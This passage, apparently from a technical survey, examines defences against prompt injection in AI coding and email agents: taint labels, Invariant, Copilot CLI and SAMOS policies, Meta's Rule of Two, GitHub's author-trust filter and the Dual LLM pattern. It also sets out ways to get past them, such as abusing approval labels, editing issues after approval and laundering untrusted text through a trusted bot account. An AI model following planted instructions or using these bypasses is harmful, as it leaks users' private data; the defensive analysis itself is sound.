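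Invariant's own remedy is a policy for its product Guardrails, and it uses no integrity label. The policy compares the repository and owner named in each call with those in earlier calls. If either differs, it raises a violation with the message "You can access only one repo per session." In the attack it would refuse `get_file_contents` on the first repository other than Pacman, so no private text would reach the model. The agent can still make a legitimate fix to the Pacman game without asking the user, but she can't have it consult another of her projects in the same session. A malicious issue could still lead the agent to damage the Pacman code, because that attack would stay within one repository.

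Microsoft and GitHub built an experimental form of session taint into GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal. A user turns it on by starting the program with `FIDES_IFC=true`. The program then keeps a context label, updates it whenever a tool returns a result, and uses it to label each tool call as a whole. The GitHub MCP server can supply the labels for its own results.

Copilot CLI's context label records confidentiality as well as integrity, which makes the rule much less restrictive. In Microsoft's version of the attack, an outsider opens a public issue asking for information from the private repository `contoso/core` to be posted as a comment. Reading the issue makes the context untrusted and public. Reading `contoso/core` then makes it untrusted and private, and the policy prevents an agent in that state from posting in public. An agent fixing a genuine bug reported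 in a public issue never reads anything private, so it can finish without asking anyone. Microsoft reports that work confined to public repositories, or to private ones, can finish without human intervention. However, the policy Microsoft describes for this case would also let an agent commit harmful code to the same public repository if an issue persuaded it to.

Copilot CLI enforces these policies only for selected tools from the GitHub MCP server, and not yet for tools from other MCP servers. An agent that also has a chat tool could therefore leak data through it without breaking any of the policies.

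Ntousakis's system, SAMOS, puts the check outside the agent. The user replaces the MCP servers in her application's settings with a single *gateway*, a program that relays every call between the application and the servers. Each tool has two annotations, `read_confidentiality` and `write_confidentiality`, each set to high or low. A tool that reads private repositories has a high read level, and one that writes to public repositories has a low write level. The tool's developer supplies these annotations, and whoever deploys the tool can change them. Optional annotations describe what else a tool can do, such as use the network or the file system. A policy can then let data flow from a high tool to a low one only if the low tool can use neither the network nor the file system.

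The gateway sets the session's level from the first tool call. In the replay, `list_issues` reads a public repository, so the session's level becomes low. The agent then follows the planted instructions and tries to read a private repository, whose level is high, and SAMOS blocks the request. This stops the attack one stage earlier than an integrity label would, before the private text reaches the model.

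It is odd that this works, because both annotations concern secrecy, while the attack starts with untrusted content. An ordinary confidentiality rule allows an agent to read a public issue and then a private file. It marks the session private after the second read and blocks the later write to a public place, which would also have prevented the leak. SAMOS blocks the private read instead, in effect treating "public" as if it meant "a stranger may have written this". That is often true on GitHub, since anyone can comment on a public project.

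In other cases, outsiders can't edit public data or can add to private data. A company's published price list is public, but outsiders can't edit it, so an agent that had read it would needlessly lose access to private files. A mailbox is private, but strangers can send email to it. A session that began with the mailbox would be high, and nothing in the SAMOS scheme would stop a planted email from getting the agent to alter or delete other private files, since high data would only be flowing to high places. Ntousakis designed SAMOS to prevent data leakage, so this is a limit of its purpose as much as a defect.

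The thesis is also unclear about how the session's confidentiality level changes. It describes each tool interaction as updating the session to the new level, which would let a private read raise a low session to high. Stopping the attack would then depend on a later check on writing. In the worked example, however, the private read is itself a violation, so the system refuses it.

Ntousakis acknowledges a further difficulty with labelling tools instead of data. `get_file_contents` reads both public and private repositories, so no fixed annotation fits it. He suggests either changing the tool to return the confidentiality of what it read, or splitting it into `get_public_file` and `get_private_file`. The first option requires new server code and amounts to labelling data, while the second relies on the agent's planner to pick the right tool.

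The only evidence for SAMOS is this case study. Ntousakis claims that it blocks the attack while preserving the original functionality, but he did not count how many ordinary tasks still work, and he tried no attack designed to get around the gateway. He names manual annotation and the two-level scale as the main limitations. If an agent in a high session needs something public, he proposes that a different agent fetch it in a separate low session.

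The table applies each rule, as its designers describe it, to three harmless jobs.

| Job in a single session | One integrity label | Invariant's rule | Copilot CLI | SAMOS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read a public issue, commit a fix to the same repository | Stops at the commit | Runs | Runs | Runs |
| Read a public issue, consult a private design note, save a plan beside the note | Stops at the save | Stops at the private read | Runs | Stops at the private read |
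| Read one private repository, write to another | Runs | Stops at the write | Runs | Runs |

Copilot CLI does best on these jobs because it tracks the most. The single integrity label blocks the most common of the three jobs, but it is the only rule in the table that would stop a planted issue from getting harmful code into the public repository.

### The lethal trifecta and the Agents Rule of Two

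Willison uses the term *lethal trifecta* for the combination that made the GitHub attack possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. He had worried about users connecting several MCP servers that together supply all three, but GitHub's server supplied them by itself. Vendors usually respond to such an exploit by closing the channel that carried the data out, but they can't do that for a combination of tools that the user put together. He advises users to avoid the combination entirely.

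Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this advice into a rule for developers. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session:

- [A] it can process untrustworthy inputs;
- [B] it can access sensitive systems or private data;
- [C] it can change state or communicate externally.

If a job needs all three and the agent can't start again with a fresh context, Meta calls for supervision, through human approval or another reliable check. To bring the GitHub agent within the rule, a developer could show it only issues from people she trusts, which removes [A], or give it a key that works only for the public repository, which removes [B]. She could also keep [A] and [B] and have a person approve every write, which controls [C].

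As a design rule, this involves no tracking, because the developer sets the agent's properties before it starts. Meta also allows the configuration to change during a session, and the rule then behaves like session taint. For example, an agent may browse the internet while it can communicate, then lose that ability before it opens internal systems. Meta calls this a one-way switch. The untrusted pages are still in the context, so restoring communication would complete the trifecta.

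Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, at first welcomed the rule because it covers changes of state, whereas his trifecta covers only data theft. But Meta's diagram marked the combination of untrustworthy inputs and the ability to change state as "safe", and he soon objected, posting as simonw in an online discussion, that this combination can do harm without any private data. Andrew Bullen of Stripe agrees that untrusted content and the ability to take a sensitive action are enough to cause harm, according to notes on his talk, *Breaking the Lethal Trifecta (Without Ruining Your Agents)*. He calls the pair the "lethal bifecta" and recommends human review of every sensitive action.

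At a 2026 conference, Ariel Fogel, a researcher at Pillar Security and a contributor to the security organisation OWASP, called both the trifecta and Meta's rule helpful for limiting damage. He added that research has already shown attacks working with only two of the properties present, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Infosecurity Europe* (2026). The article does not identify the research, so his remark is weaker evidence than the examples anyone can construct from the rule itself.

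In one such attack, an issue persuades an agent to add harmful code to a public library, using a key that gives access to nothing else. The agent has [A] and [C]. Whether it also has [B] depends on what "sensitive systems" means. If the phrase covers only systems that hold secrets, the agent satisfies the rule and the attack succeeds. If it covers any system where a change would matter, a library that other people install is sensitive, so the agent has all three properties and a person must approve the commit. Meta intended the broader meaning and changed the diagram after Willison objected. Under that meaning, the rule requires approval for the same action as a single integrity label does.

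Meta does not present the rule as sufficient. The rule does not cover an agent's own mistakes, excessive privileges or misinformation in the agent's answers, and a design that follows it can still fail if a user confirms a warning without reading it. Meta also concedes that the rule is a bad fit for some of the most wanted uses, such as background agents, where stopping for a person's approval is disruptive or ineffective. For these uses it is researching oversight agents that could give the approval, but that would return the decision to a model, which an attacker might also mislead.

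## Separate integrity and confidentiality labels

Copilot CLI's second label tracks confidentiality, so the software can distinguish an agent that has only read strangers' text from one that has also seen something private. Each label still covers the whole session. A confidentiality label can also catch leaks that involve no attacker, as in Microsoft's mailbox example.

### Alex's mailbox

Alex asks an agent to handle the unanswered emails in an inbox. Priya has sent a preview of the quarterly sales. Marco has also written, and he is curious about the figures but isn't allowed to see them yet. Nobody has planted malicious instructions in the emails, but a model trying to be helpful could still send Marco Priya's numbers.

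Microsoft labels each email with the people who may read it. Once the agent has read both, the label of anything it writes is the intersection of the two sets:

```
Priya's email    {Alex, Priya}
Marco's email    {Alex, Marco}
the reply        {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}
```

Marco isn't in the result, so the software won't send him the reply unless Alex approves it. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, its label would have been {Alex, Priya, Marco} and the reply's label {Alex, Marco}. The agent could then answer Marco without Alex's approval, because he would already have the numbers.

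The rule depends only on who could read the sources, so even a reply telling Marco to wait for the announcement would need approval. So would a thank-you note to Priya, because she wasn't a reader of Marco's email. Copying Marco on the sales figures would make the reader set {Alex, Marco}. The agent could then discuss the figures with Marco without approval, but not with Priya, who supplied them.

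### Four combinations in one session

With two levels for each label, a session is always in one of four states. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, arrange them as a diamond, with the least restricted state at the bottom:

```
              untrusted, private
             /                  \
  untrusted, public        trusted, private
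             \                  /
               trusted, public
```

Reading a stranger's text moves the session up one side, and reading a private file moves it up the other. Neither of the two middle states is more restrictive than the other, so no single scale can represent all four. For an agent that wants to post in a public channel, they call for different treatment:

| Session label | How the session got there | Posting to a public channel |
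|---|---|---|
| Trusted, public | It has only the user's request | Allow |
| Untrusted, public | It read a stranger's issue | Allow a comment, since there is nothing private to leak. Ask a person about a change that others will rely on, such as code |
| Trusted, private | It read the user's private design note | Microsoft's rule allows this. Asking a person is safer, because the model may have misunderstood what to publish |
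| Untrusted, private | It read both, or one email from a stranger | Ask a person, or block if nobody is available |

A planted instruction can leak private data only when the session is both untrusted and private, the state the GitHub issue attack reached. An integrity label alone would stop posts in both untrusted rows, and a confidentiality label alone would stop them in both private rows. With both labels, a designer can stop posts in just the last row, without tracking individual pieces of data.

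How much separate labels help depends on the data sources. GitHub's server labels public repositories untrusted and public, and private ones trusted and private, so an agent that reads only one kind stays in one of the diamond's two middle states. An email from a stranger is both untrusted and private, so reading one moves an agent straight from the bottom of the diamond to the top. Reader sets help here because the stranger is a permitted reader of their own email, so the agent can reply to it.

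*From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (Hegelich, Sarhan and colleagues, 2026) compared one label with two for coding agents. The study scripted twelve ordinary programming workflows and twelve attacks, each with five steps, and ran the tool calls through different checkers. One checker set a single flag when the agent read anything untrusted or sensitive, then blocked file writes, test runs and network access. Another tracked trust and sensitivity separately. Both stopped all twelve attacks, but the single flag also stopped the ten ordinary workflows that began with outside material, such as an issue or a crash log, while the separate labels stopped no ordinary workflows.

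The second label was not the only reason the two-part checker did better. The checker also had an intermediate trust level, which an issue reaches once the agent has summarised it and which permits editing and isolated tests. At the plain untrusted level the agent may only inspect local files, so without the intermediate level most of the ten workflows would have stopped even with the second label. At least one workflow relied on an explicit declassification, which the design reserves for the human operator. The test did not involve a model, and with only twelve workflows, the 95% interval for the share wrongly blocked runs from zero to 26%.

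### Microsoft's rule for a Teams message

Microsoft has published a policy for posting to a channel in Teams, its workplace chat program. The software goes through these tests in order:

```
1. if the context is trusted:              allow
2. missing = channel members − permitted readers of the text
   if missing is empty:                    allow
3. otherwise:                              ask, listing the missing people
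```

The last line denies any call that the earlier lines don't decide. For the second test, the software fetches the channel's current membership from Teams, so neither the model nor an attacker can misstate who is in the channel. People who join later may still be able to read the message.

The policy lets a message through if it passes a test of either the integrity of the context or the confidentiality of the text. In Microsoft's sample call, the context is untrusted, so the call fails the integrity test. The text, which says that a new model will be announced on Friday, has two permitted readers. If they are the only members of the group receiving the message, it passes the confidentiality test and goes through. If there is a third member, the software asks the user about that person. This question is easier to answer than a general request to approve a tool call, although the published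 version lists account identifiers, which a real dialog would have to replace with names.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) applies the same logic to tools in general. A tool that sends data out needs to satisfy only one of Costa and colleagues' two rules, integrity or confidentiality. Other consequential actions, such as deleting a file, must satisfy the integrity rule, because knowing who may read a file doesn't make it safe to delete.

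Writing a policy for each tool makes room for details like the membership lookup. But *SPA* (2026) points out that the guarantee then depends on every policy being correct and complete, whereas a single flow rule applies everywhere.

### Robust declassification

The first line of the Teams policy deliberately lets private text go to anyone, provided the context is trusted. People often send private information on purpose, and a rule that never let private data influence an outgoing message would stop a user from sending a draft contract to a new client. The principle behind the line is *robust declassification*, which allows a release of private data only when untrusted content could not have caused it.

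Myers and colleagues define it by what attackers can affect. They must have no influence over what information a system releases or over whether it releases any. An attacker who interferes then learns no more than one who only watches. The paper's example, with simpler variable names, is a single line:

```
if x then y := declassify(z)
```

Here `z` is secret, `y` is public and `declassify` releases the secret intentionally. An attacker who can set `x` controls whether the release happens, and one who can get a different secret copied into `z` controls what is released. The release is robust only if the attacker can change neither variable. *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real--Ideal Paradigm* (2026) gives a shorter example of a violation, `p := u * s`, where `p` is public, `u` is untrusted and `s` is secret. An attacker who sets `u` to 1 learns the secret, while setting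 it to 0 reveals nothing.

In an agent, the context corresponds to `x`, because the model uses it to decide whether to send, and the message text corresponds to `z`. The first line of the Teams policy tests only the context. That is enough under session taint, where the text comes from the same context, but with value labels the text can have its own label, which this line does not check.

Suppose the user asks the agent to post a summary of today's mail in the team channel. The software keeps the emails out of the context and has a separate model call write the summary. The context is still trusted, so the software posts the summary without checking whether everyone in the channel may read the emails. A planted email couldn't have caused the posting, but it could have caused the separate model to include a salary from another email. Kolluri and colleagues' version of the rule can prevent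 this, because it also lets a designer require particular arguments to be trusted.

Full robustness is often too strict, as Myers and colleagues acknowledge. An agent that answers mail releases information because outsiders wrote to it, so outsiders always have some influence over whether it releases anything. Myers and colleagues therefore add explicit endorsement, which allows untrusted input a limited influence. Alex endorses Marco's request in this sense by approving a reply to it.

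### Clearing one label at a time

Because of label creep, a system needs ways to lower its labels. If it keeps separate integrity and confidentiality labels, an operation that lowers one must not change the other. Hegelich and colleagues apply this rule in ActiveSecHarness, a layer of checks between a coding agent and the computer it works on. Its session label has a trust part with four levels (Trusted, Sanitized, Derived and Untrusted) and a sensitivity part that is either Public or Sensitive.

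*Sanitisation* cleans up the form of a text, for example by stripping invisible characters that make code look different to a person than to a compiler. It changes the trust part to Sanitized and leaves the sensitivity part unchanged. *Redaction* replaces secrets such as passwords with meaningless fingerprints. Only redaction or an explicit waiver from the operator can return the sensitivity part to Public.

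Suppose an agent reads an issue filed by a stranger and then a settings file that contains a password. If sanitising the issue also cleared the confidentiality label, the agent could send the password out. If redacting the password also cleared the integrity label, the agent could follow the stranger's instructions as though the user had written them.

A single scale would lose this distinction. ActiveSecHarness uses a five-step scale for its quick check on each call, with Sensitive above Untrusted. On that scale, the session in the example is Sensitive, and after redaction there would be no record that the agent had also read a stranger's issue. The system therefore keeps both labels in a ledger that covers agents and the files they share. If one agent writes a secret to a file and a second agent reads it, the second inherits the label and can't send the contents out.

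The trust part of the label is too easy to lower. Stripping invisible characters does not remove an instruction written in plain English, and a model's summary of a malicious issue may repeat the instruction. ActiveSecHarness limits the damage by refusing network access and arbitrary commands at the Derived level. The agent can still edit files at that level, so a malicious issue could get bad code into the project.

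Kolluri and colleagues give users different ways of lowering the two labels. Their agent, Prudentia, can ask the user to endorse a piece of untrusted data. They left out an equivalent for confidentiality because whether a release is appropriate depends heavily on the situation. Instead, the user approves individual calls, so permission to send a contract to one client doesn't make it available to everyone.

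### Shrinking reader sets and honest mistakes

A reader set never grows as the agent reads more. After two emails, the reader set for Alex's agent had shrunk to {Alex}. If the agent read twenty emails from twenty people before replying, it would need approval for every reply. A fresh session for each email would avoid this, but the agent could no longer use one email to answer another. Reader sets work better for material with a wide audience, since a summary of two documents that the whole company may read can also go to the whole company.

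In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) try to recover some of the lost replies. Their system, FlowSeal, also releases a summary of two records only to someone authorised to see both. But before blocking a message to someone without authorisation, it shows the protected records and the proposed text to a separate model, which answers SAFE or BLOCKED. A note telling Marco to wait could pass this test.

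In Shim and colleagues' tests, FlowSeal leaked between 0 and 3.3% of the sensitive items and completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best other defence they tested. Their confidentiality proof excludes cases where the checker wrongly answers SAFE, so part of the guarantee again depends on a model's judgement.

Integrity checks can miss a model's own mistakes. Costa and colleagues note that a model can misread the user or make an unnecessary call even when all its data is trusted, with consequences similar to those of an attack. Suppose a user asks an agent to post a progress update in a channel, and the agent mentions planned redundancies it read about in a trusted board paper. No untrusted content is involved, so the Teams policy allows the message without checking whether contractors are in the channel.

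The mailbox has the same weakness. A company might reasonably treat email from its own staff as trusted. If its mail tool then used the Teams rule, the agent could send Priya's figures to Marco, because the software would allow the email without comparing readers.

Putting the reader test first would not help, since passing either test is enough. The designer would have to remove the trusted-context line, and a user who does want a new client to see a contract would then have to answer a question. That seems reasonable for messages that leave the company. ActiveSecHarness is stricter and blocks network access from any sensitive session, even a trusted one, until someone redacts the secret or waives the rule.

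*An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and Tsai, 2026) replaces the trust test with the user's own permissions. Its system, GAAP, asks users how their private data may be shared and checks every disclosure against their answers. It doesn't assume that the model, or even the user's prompt, is free of attacks. Stanley and colleagues report that GAAP blocked every disclosure attack they tried, but completed slightly fewer tasks.

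Checking only the text of a message can also miss a leak. In one of Shim and colleagues' scenarios, Jane's agent has Mark's mental health diagnosis, and his ex-wife Emily wants to know it. Emily sets up a shared page of true and false entries about Mark and asks the agent to delete the false ones. The agent writes nothing sensitive, but the remaining entries reveal the diagnosis to Emily.

This attack and two others that also used ordinary requests extracted between 43.8% and 75.6% of the sensitive items from an agent whose only defence was a carefully written prompt. An integrity label would help if the software treated Emily's messages as untrusted, but a designer may be tempted to trust a known contact. A reader test applies only to outgoing text, so it doesn't help when the agent only deletes. A confidentiality label on the whole session catches the leak, because the agent had read Mark's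 records before it changed the page.

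## GitHub Agentic Workflows and filtering by author trust

Most of the rules so far let an agent read a stranger's text and then restrict what it does next. GitHub also offers software that removes untrusted text before the model receives it and lets the agent keep its permissions. This is close to Biba's strict integrity policy, which prohibits a program from reading data below its own integrity level.

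The filter is part of GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs coding agents inside GitHub Actions, GitHub's system for running jobs automatically when something happens in a repository. A *maintainer*, someone who looks after a project, describes the job in plain English in a text file with settings at the top. Rojas (2026), in *GitHub Agentic Workflows open source tool reaches general availability*, dates the general release to 28 October 2026.

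These jobs often run unattended, so the software can't stop and ask about a doubtful action. With filtering, the maintainer decides beforehand whose text the agent may read. *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group, GitHub Next, explains why the filter judges authors instead of wording. Attackers rephrase their instructions or split them across several fields, and a maintainer who keeps tightening a text filter eventually blocks too much legitimate text.

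### Labelling an item by its author

The agent reads issues, comments and pull requests through the MCP gateway, which relays its calls as the gateway in SAMOS does. When the agent asks for a list of issues, the gateway fetches the list, gives each issue an integrity level and removes every issue below the workflow's minimum. The model receives what remains. GitHub uses five levels, from highest to lowest:

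| Level | Items at this level |
|---|---|
| `merged` | Merged pull requests, and commits on the project's main branch, whoever wrote them |
| `approved` | Items by owners, members and collaborators; pull requests from a branch of the public repository itself, not from an outsider's copy; everything in a private repository; items by recognised bots |
| `unapproved` | Items by contributors and first-time contributors |
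| `none` | Everything else, including items by people with no earlier connection to the project |
| `blocked` | Items by users whom the maintainers have blocked |

A maintainer can set the minimum to any of the top four levels. Setting it to `none` admits everyone except blocked users. By default, a public repository has a minimum of `approved` and a private one has no filter.

An item's level can rise without any change to its text. An outsider's pull request starts at `unapproved` or `none` and rises to `merged` once a maintainer merges it. The new level shows that someone with authority accepted the change, so its reliability depends on how well that person reviewed it.

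The gateway logs a `DIFC_FILTERED` event for each item it removes, with the tool, the author and the reason. DIFC stands for *decentralized information flow control*, the line of security research behind the gateway's rules.

### The read and write rules

GitHub Next states the rules as comparisons between sets of tags. Each item and each agent has a secrecy label (here called a confidentiality label) and an integrity label.

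```
an agent may read an item if
    secrecy(item)     ⊆  secrecy(agent)
    integrity(item)   ⊇  integrity(agent)

an agent may write to a destination if
    secrecy(agent)    ⊆  secrecy(destination)
    integrity(agent)  ⊇  integrity(destination)
```

For reads, the agent's integrity label is the workflow's minimum integrity label. These labels list marks of trust, so a longer list means higher integrity, whereas a longer list of possible writers would mean lower integrity.

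The levels fit this scheme if each one carries the tags of the levels below it. Suppose the minimum is `approved`, so the agent's integrity label is {unapproved, approved}. A collaborator's comment has the same two tags, and a merged commit has those and one more, so the agent may read both. A past contributor's issue has only {unapproved}, so the gateway removes it.

Under the full rules, an agent with a private repository's tag in its secrecy label could not write to a public issue, because the issue lacks that tag. GitHub Next describes the secrecy half of the rules as unfinished, since the product tracks secrecy but doesn't yet use it to prevent leaks between repositories.

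The gateway's code could also apply session taint. Its documentation on pkg.go.dev, a public index of Go software, lists three modes. Suppose an agent whose minimum is `approved` asks for ten issues, three from strangers, and then tries to write to a destination that requires `approved`.

| Mode | The read | Agent's integrity label | The write |
|---|---|---|---|
| Strict | Blocked | Unchanged | Allowed |
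| Filter | Seven issues arrive | Unchanged | Allowed |
| Propagate | All ten arrive | Loses the `approved` tag | Blocked |

Propagate mode joins labels by taking the union of the secrecy labels and the intersection of the integrity labels. The integrity part is Biba's low-water-mark rule. Filter mode avoids self-revocation because nothing the agent reads through the gateway can lower its label.

### Guards

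The code that compares the sets treats a tag such as `approved:myorg/web-app` as a plain string, so it needs no GitHub-specific logic. A separate component, the *guard*, contains the rules for one data source. The GitHub guard reads the arguments of a tool call and the metadata returned with the response, such as each author's relationship to the repository, and returns tags.

This division limits the work of adding another source. To filter tickets from the issue tracker Jira, for example, a developer has to write a guard that distinguishes staff tickets from customer tickets, but doesn't have to change the comparison code. Mistakes are most likely in the new guard. If it gives customer tickets the tags meant for staff, the filter will admit hostile text even though every later comparison is correct.

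A guard labels parts of a response by their position. It can mark the first item in a list as public and untrusted and the second as private and verified, without copying either. Parts it doesn't label get the guard's default label or, if it has none, the label of the whole response. A poorly chosen default would cause the same problem as Ruby's unmarked web queries.

These are value labels, but GitHub uses them to filter items before the model runs. The agent receives ordinary text, and every item that passed the filter meets the same minimum integrity level. However the model mixes those items, the join of their integrity labels can't fall below that minimum. GitHub therefore gets per-item precision without having to work out which inputs influenced an output, but only by withholding items below the minimum from the agent.

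### Admitting an outsider's report

If the player who wrote the report about the Pacman ghosts has never contributed to the project, the report sits at `none`, and a code-maintenance agent with a minimum of `approved` won't receive it. A maintainer can read the report and add a tag to it on GitHub, such as `human-reviewed`, that the workflow's settings list as an approval label. On the next run, the gateway raises the report to `approved` and the agent can work on it. The endorsement covers only this report, and the player's other posts stay at `none`.

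GitHub's *MCP Gateway Specification* fixes the order in which such exceptions apply:

```
base = level from author, merge status and repository visibility

if the author is in blocked-users:       level = blocked
else if the item has a refusal label:    level = none
else if the author is in trusted-users:  level = max(base, approved)
else if the item has an approval label:  level = max(base, approved)
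else:                                    level = base

remove the item if level < the workflow's minimum
```

A refusal label lets a maintainer hide a particular item, even one that a colleague wrote or approved. The label lowers the item only to `none`, so a workflow that accepts everything will still receive it.

Maintainers can also turn on an option to approve items with a thumbs-up or heart and to reject them with a thumbs-down. The gateway counts a reaction only if the person who left it has a high enough level, by default `approved`.

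The specification checks whether an item has an approval label, but not who applied it. On GitHub, people need some level of permission in a project to add labels, but automated jobs can add them too. GitHub Next's example of an approval label is `triaged`, which a triage agent might be told to apply. An attacker could then use an issue to trick the triage agent into labeling it, and the code-writing agent would receive the issue as approved. Maintainers should allow only people to apply the approval label.

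An author can also edit an issue after a maintainer has approved it. The specification has no step that withdraws approval when the text changes, so an attacker could submit an honest report, wait for the approval label and then add malicious instructions.

### A code-maintenance agent

An agent might tidy the Pacman code every night and propose its changes as pull requests. It would read the existing code, which is already at `merged`, and perhaps the maintainers' comments about what they want, which are at `approved`. It would have little use for strangers' comments, so a high minimum level would barely limit its work.

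The attack on Claude Desktop would fail against this agent at the first call, because the list of open issues would leave out the attacker's issue and the agent would never receive the instruction to look at private repositories. Session taint stopped the same attack at the last call and left the decision to a person. With filtering, nobody has to decide, and the agent can still open its pull request.

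Filtering also makes the agent cheaper to run. GitHub's *Example*, a guide to automated repository maintenance, notes that removed items never enter the context, which can dramatically reduce its size on a busy public project. GitHub gives no measurements of that saving or of how many attacks and useful reports the filter removes.

### A triage agent and its safe outputs

A triage agent reads new bug reports, sorts them and replies to their authors. Many of those authors are strangers, so a minimum trust level of `approved` would filter out most of the reports, and the maintainer has to lower the minimum.

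GitHub's guide recommends a triage workflow named Repo Assist, which it describes as receiving all incoming content, including content from untrusted users. But the guide sets the minimum level to `unapproved`, which by GitHub's definitions still removes items from people with no earlier connection to the project, such as the player with the ghost report. To receive such reports, the workflow needs `none`, a setting GitHub otherwise suggests for spam detection and for jobs whose results a person reviews.

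Once the minimum is that low, the filter gives little protection, and the design relies on *safe outputs*, the name for GitHub's restrictions on what an agent can change. They work in stages:

1. The agent runs with read-only access to GitHub. When it wants to post a comment, it calls a tool that only records the request in a file.
2. After the agent has finished, a separate job gives the recorded requests to another model, which looks for leaked secrets and malicious code and can stop the run.
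3. Other jobs, each with only the write permission it needs, check the requests against the operations and quantities that the maintainer declared. They clean the text and then make the changes.

For triage, the maintainer might list only labelling and commenting as permitted actions. If a planted issue leads the agent to request a pull request, the software rejects it because pull requests aren't on the list. This resembles a session that starts out untrusted, except that a fixed list of permitted actions replaces the policy check on the session's label.

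The attacker can still misuse whatever is on the list. A hijacked triage agent could mark a serious security report as a duplicate or give its author false advice. GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026) accepts that an agent may produce plausible but inappropriate content within its limits, and recommends monitoring and periodic review. The model in the second stage might catch some of this misuse, but it has the same weakness as Meta's oversight agents.

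Comments can also expose private data. In *GitLost*, a July 2026 post for the security company Noma, Levi showed that a stranger's public issue could lead a workflow to publish text from a private repository in a comment. The workflow had read access to the organisation's other repositories and was allowed to post comments. Limits on the kind and number of outputs don't prevent a permitted comment from containing private data.

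The gateway checks secrecy labels on writes to output servers, but this check is weakest when a workflow may read all repositories, which is the setting this attack needs. GitHub's *gh-aw-mcpg* (2026), the introduction to an April version of the gateway's code, lists the secrecy labels that the output server should accept for each read setting. For a workflow that may read all repositories, the entry is a wildcard, which accepts writes from an agent with any secrecy label. GitHub's filter also covers all repositories that the agent's access key can open unless the maintainer narrows the scope. A triage agent that reads strangers' reports should therefore have a key for only the public repository.

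InfoQ's *GitHub Makes Agentic Workflows Generally Available with Isolation and Budget Controls* (2026) points out that the read-only defaults and separate write jobs don't protect a workflow if the maintainer grants the agent direct write permission or adds custom jobs.

### Reports that the agent never receives

The filter may remove the most useful report on the page. No one acts on the player's ghost bug until a maintainer notices it, which may never happen on a neglected project. Under session taint, the agent would at least have read the report and prepared a fix for someone to approve.

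The agent may also give wrong answers because the gateway removes items from a list without any notice. If a maintainer asks whether anyone has reported a crash on startup, and all three reports came from strangers, the agent will probably answer that nobody has. Threads can also stop making sense, for example when a collaborator's comment "Yes, do it the way she suggests" passes the filter but the suggestion doesn't.

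The maintainer can see from the log whether the filter removed anything. GitHub counts the removed items for each run and has a command that fetches only the runs in which the filter removed something. GitHub Next recommends starting at `approved`, reading the log and then adjusting the minimum. That helps with tuning, but someone who acts on a wrong answer has usually not read the log first. A line telling the agent how many items the filter removed would be easy to add and would contain no text from an attacker, though a stranger could change the number by posting more.

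### Hostile text from trusted authors

The filter labels an item according to the account that posted it, even if someone else wrote the text. If a collaborator pastes a customer's email into an issue, the issue is `approved`, including any instructions hidden in the email. The same would happen if a recognised bot copied release notes from someone else's package into a pull request, or if a support system filed customers' complaints as issues in a private repository, where every item counts as `approved`. This mislabelling is under-tainting, and it doesn't appear in the log because the gateway has removed nothing.

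GitHub Next acknowledges that an attacker who takes over a maintainer's account gets the maintainer's trust level. It relies on the network firewall, the agent's isolated environment and safe outputs to limit the damage.

An agent can also make untrusted text appear trusted to another agent. Suppose the triage agent summarises a stranger's issue in a comment, and the write job posts it under the account `github-actions`. GitHub's guide lists that account among the recognised bots, so by the published levels the summary is `approved`, and the code-maintenance agent may read a planted instruction that the filter had removed from the original issue. GitHub prevents this only in the memory that agents keep between runs, which it stores in a separate branch for each integrity level. Only runs at a given level write to that level's branch. Comments have no such separation, so a maintainer who runs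 both agents would do well to treat the triage agent's account as untrusted.

Some text may bypass the filter. When a new issue starts a workflow, GitHub's *Security Architecture* shows its title and body reaching the agent through a cleaning step that disables mentions of users, converts HTML tags, strips control characters and removes links to sites that aren't on a list. Like sanitisation in ActiveSecHarness, this step leaves plain-English instructions intact, and the description of this route includes no integrity check. A workflow can instead check the role of the person who triggered it before the agent starts. Web pages also bypass the filter, because the guard labels only GitHub content. If the maintainer lets the agent fetch pages from a site where strangers can write, the agent's context can contain untrusted text even with the minimum set to `merged`.

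## Quarantined readers and fresh subagent contexts

GitHub's filter protects an agent from a stranger's bug report by withholding it. If a designer wants the agent to use the report, a separate model call can read it in its own context, and the software can control what comes back. Each context is then a compartment with a single label, as in session taint. The main agent's label rises only when untrusted content enters its compartment from another.

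### The Dual LLM pattern

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes an assistant with two models and ordinary software, called the *controller*, between them. The *privileged model* takes the user's requests and can call tools. The *quarantined model* reads untrusted text and has no tools, and the designer assumes that an attacker could take it over at any moment. The controller runs the tools and keeps untrusted text in variables, so the privileged model sees only the variables' names.

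Suppose a user asks for a summary of her latest email:

1. The privileged model requests `fetch_latest_emails(1)`. The controller fetches the email and stores it as `$VAR1`.
2. The privileged model requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller passes the email to the quarantined model and stores its reply as `$VAR2`.
3. The privileged model asks the controller to display "Your latest email, summarized: $VAR2". The controller fills in the summary and shows it to the user.

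If the email contains an order to delete all her mail, the quarantined model may well repeat it, but the order is only text in `$VAR2`. The summary is as untrusted as the email, so the privileged model must never read it. Willison allowed one exception, for when the quarantined model sorts text into a fixed set of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of them and pass it to the privileged model.

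Willison called his own proposal "pretty bad". He expected it to make assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that let untrusted text reach the privileged model would undo the protection. The pattern also doesn't protect the user from being tricked, because she still reads the summary, which could persuade her to paste private data into an attacker's web page. An attacker can also spoil the summary, and Costa and colleagues give the example of an email with instructions for the quarantined model to return an empty one.

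### Microsoft's security module

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) introduced a security module for Microsoft Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. The module is based on Costa and colleagues' work, is experimental, and so far works only in Python. Like Copilot CLI, it keeps a label for the main context and checks that label before each tool call. A tool can be barred from running when the context is untrusted or exceeds a set level of confidentiality.

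The developer controls the module through one configuration object. Microsoft documents these main options:

| Option | Default | Effect |
|---|---|---|
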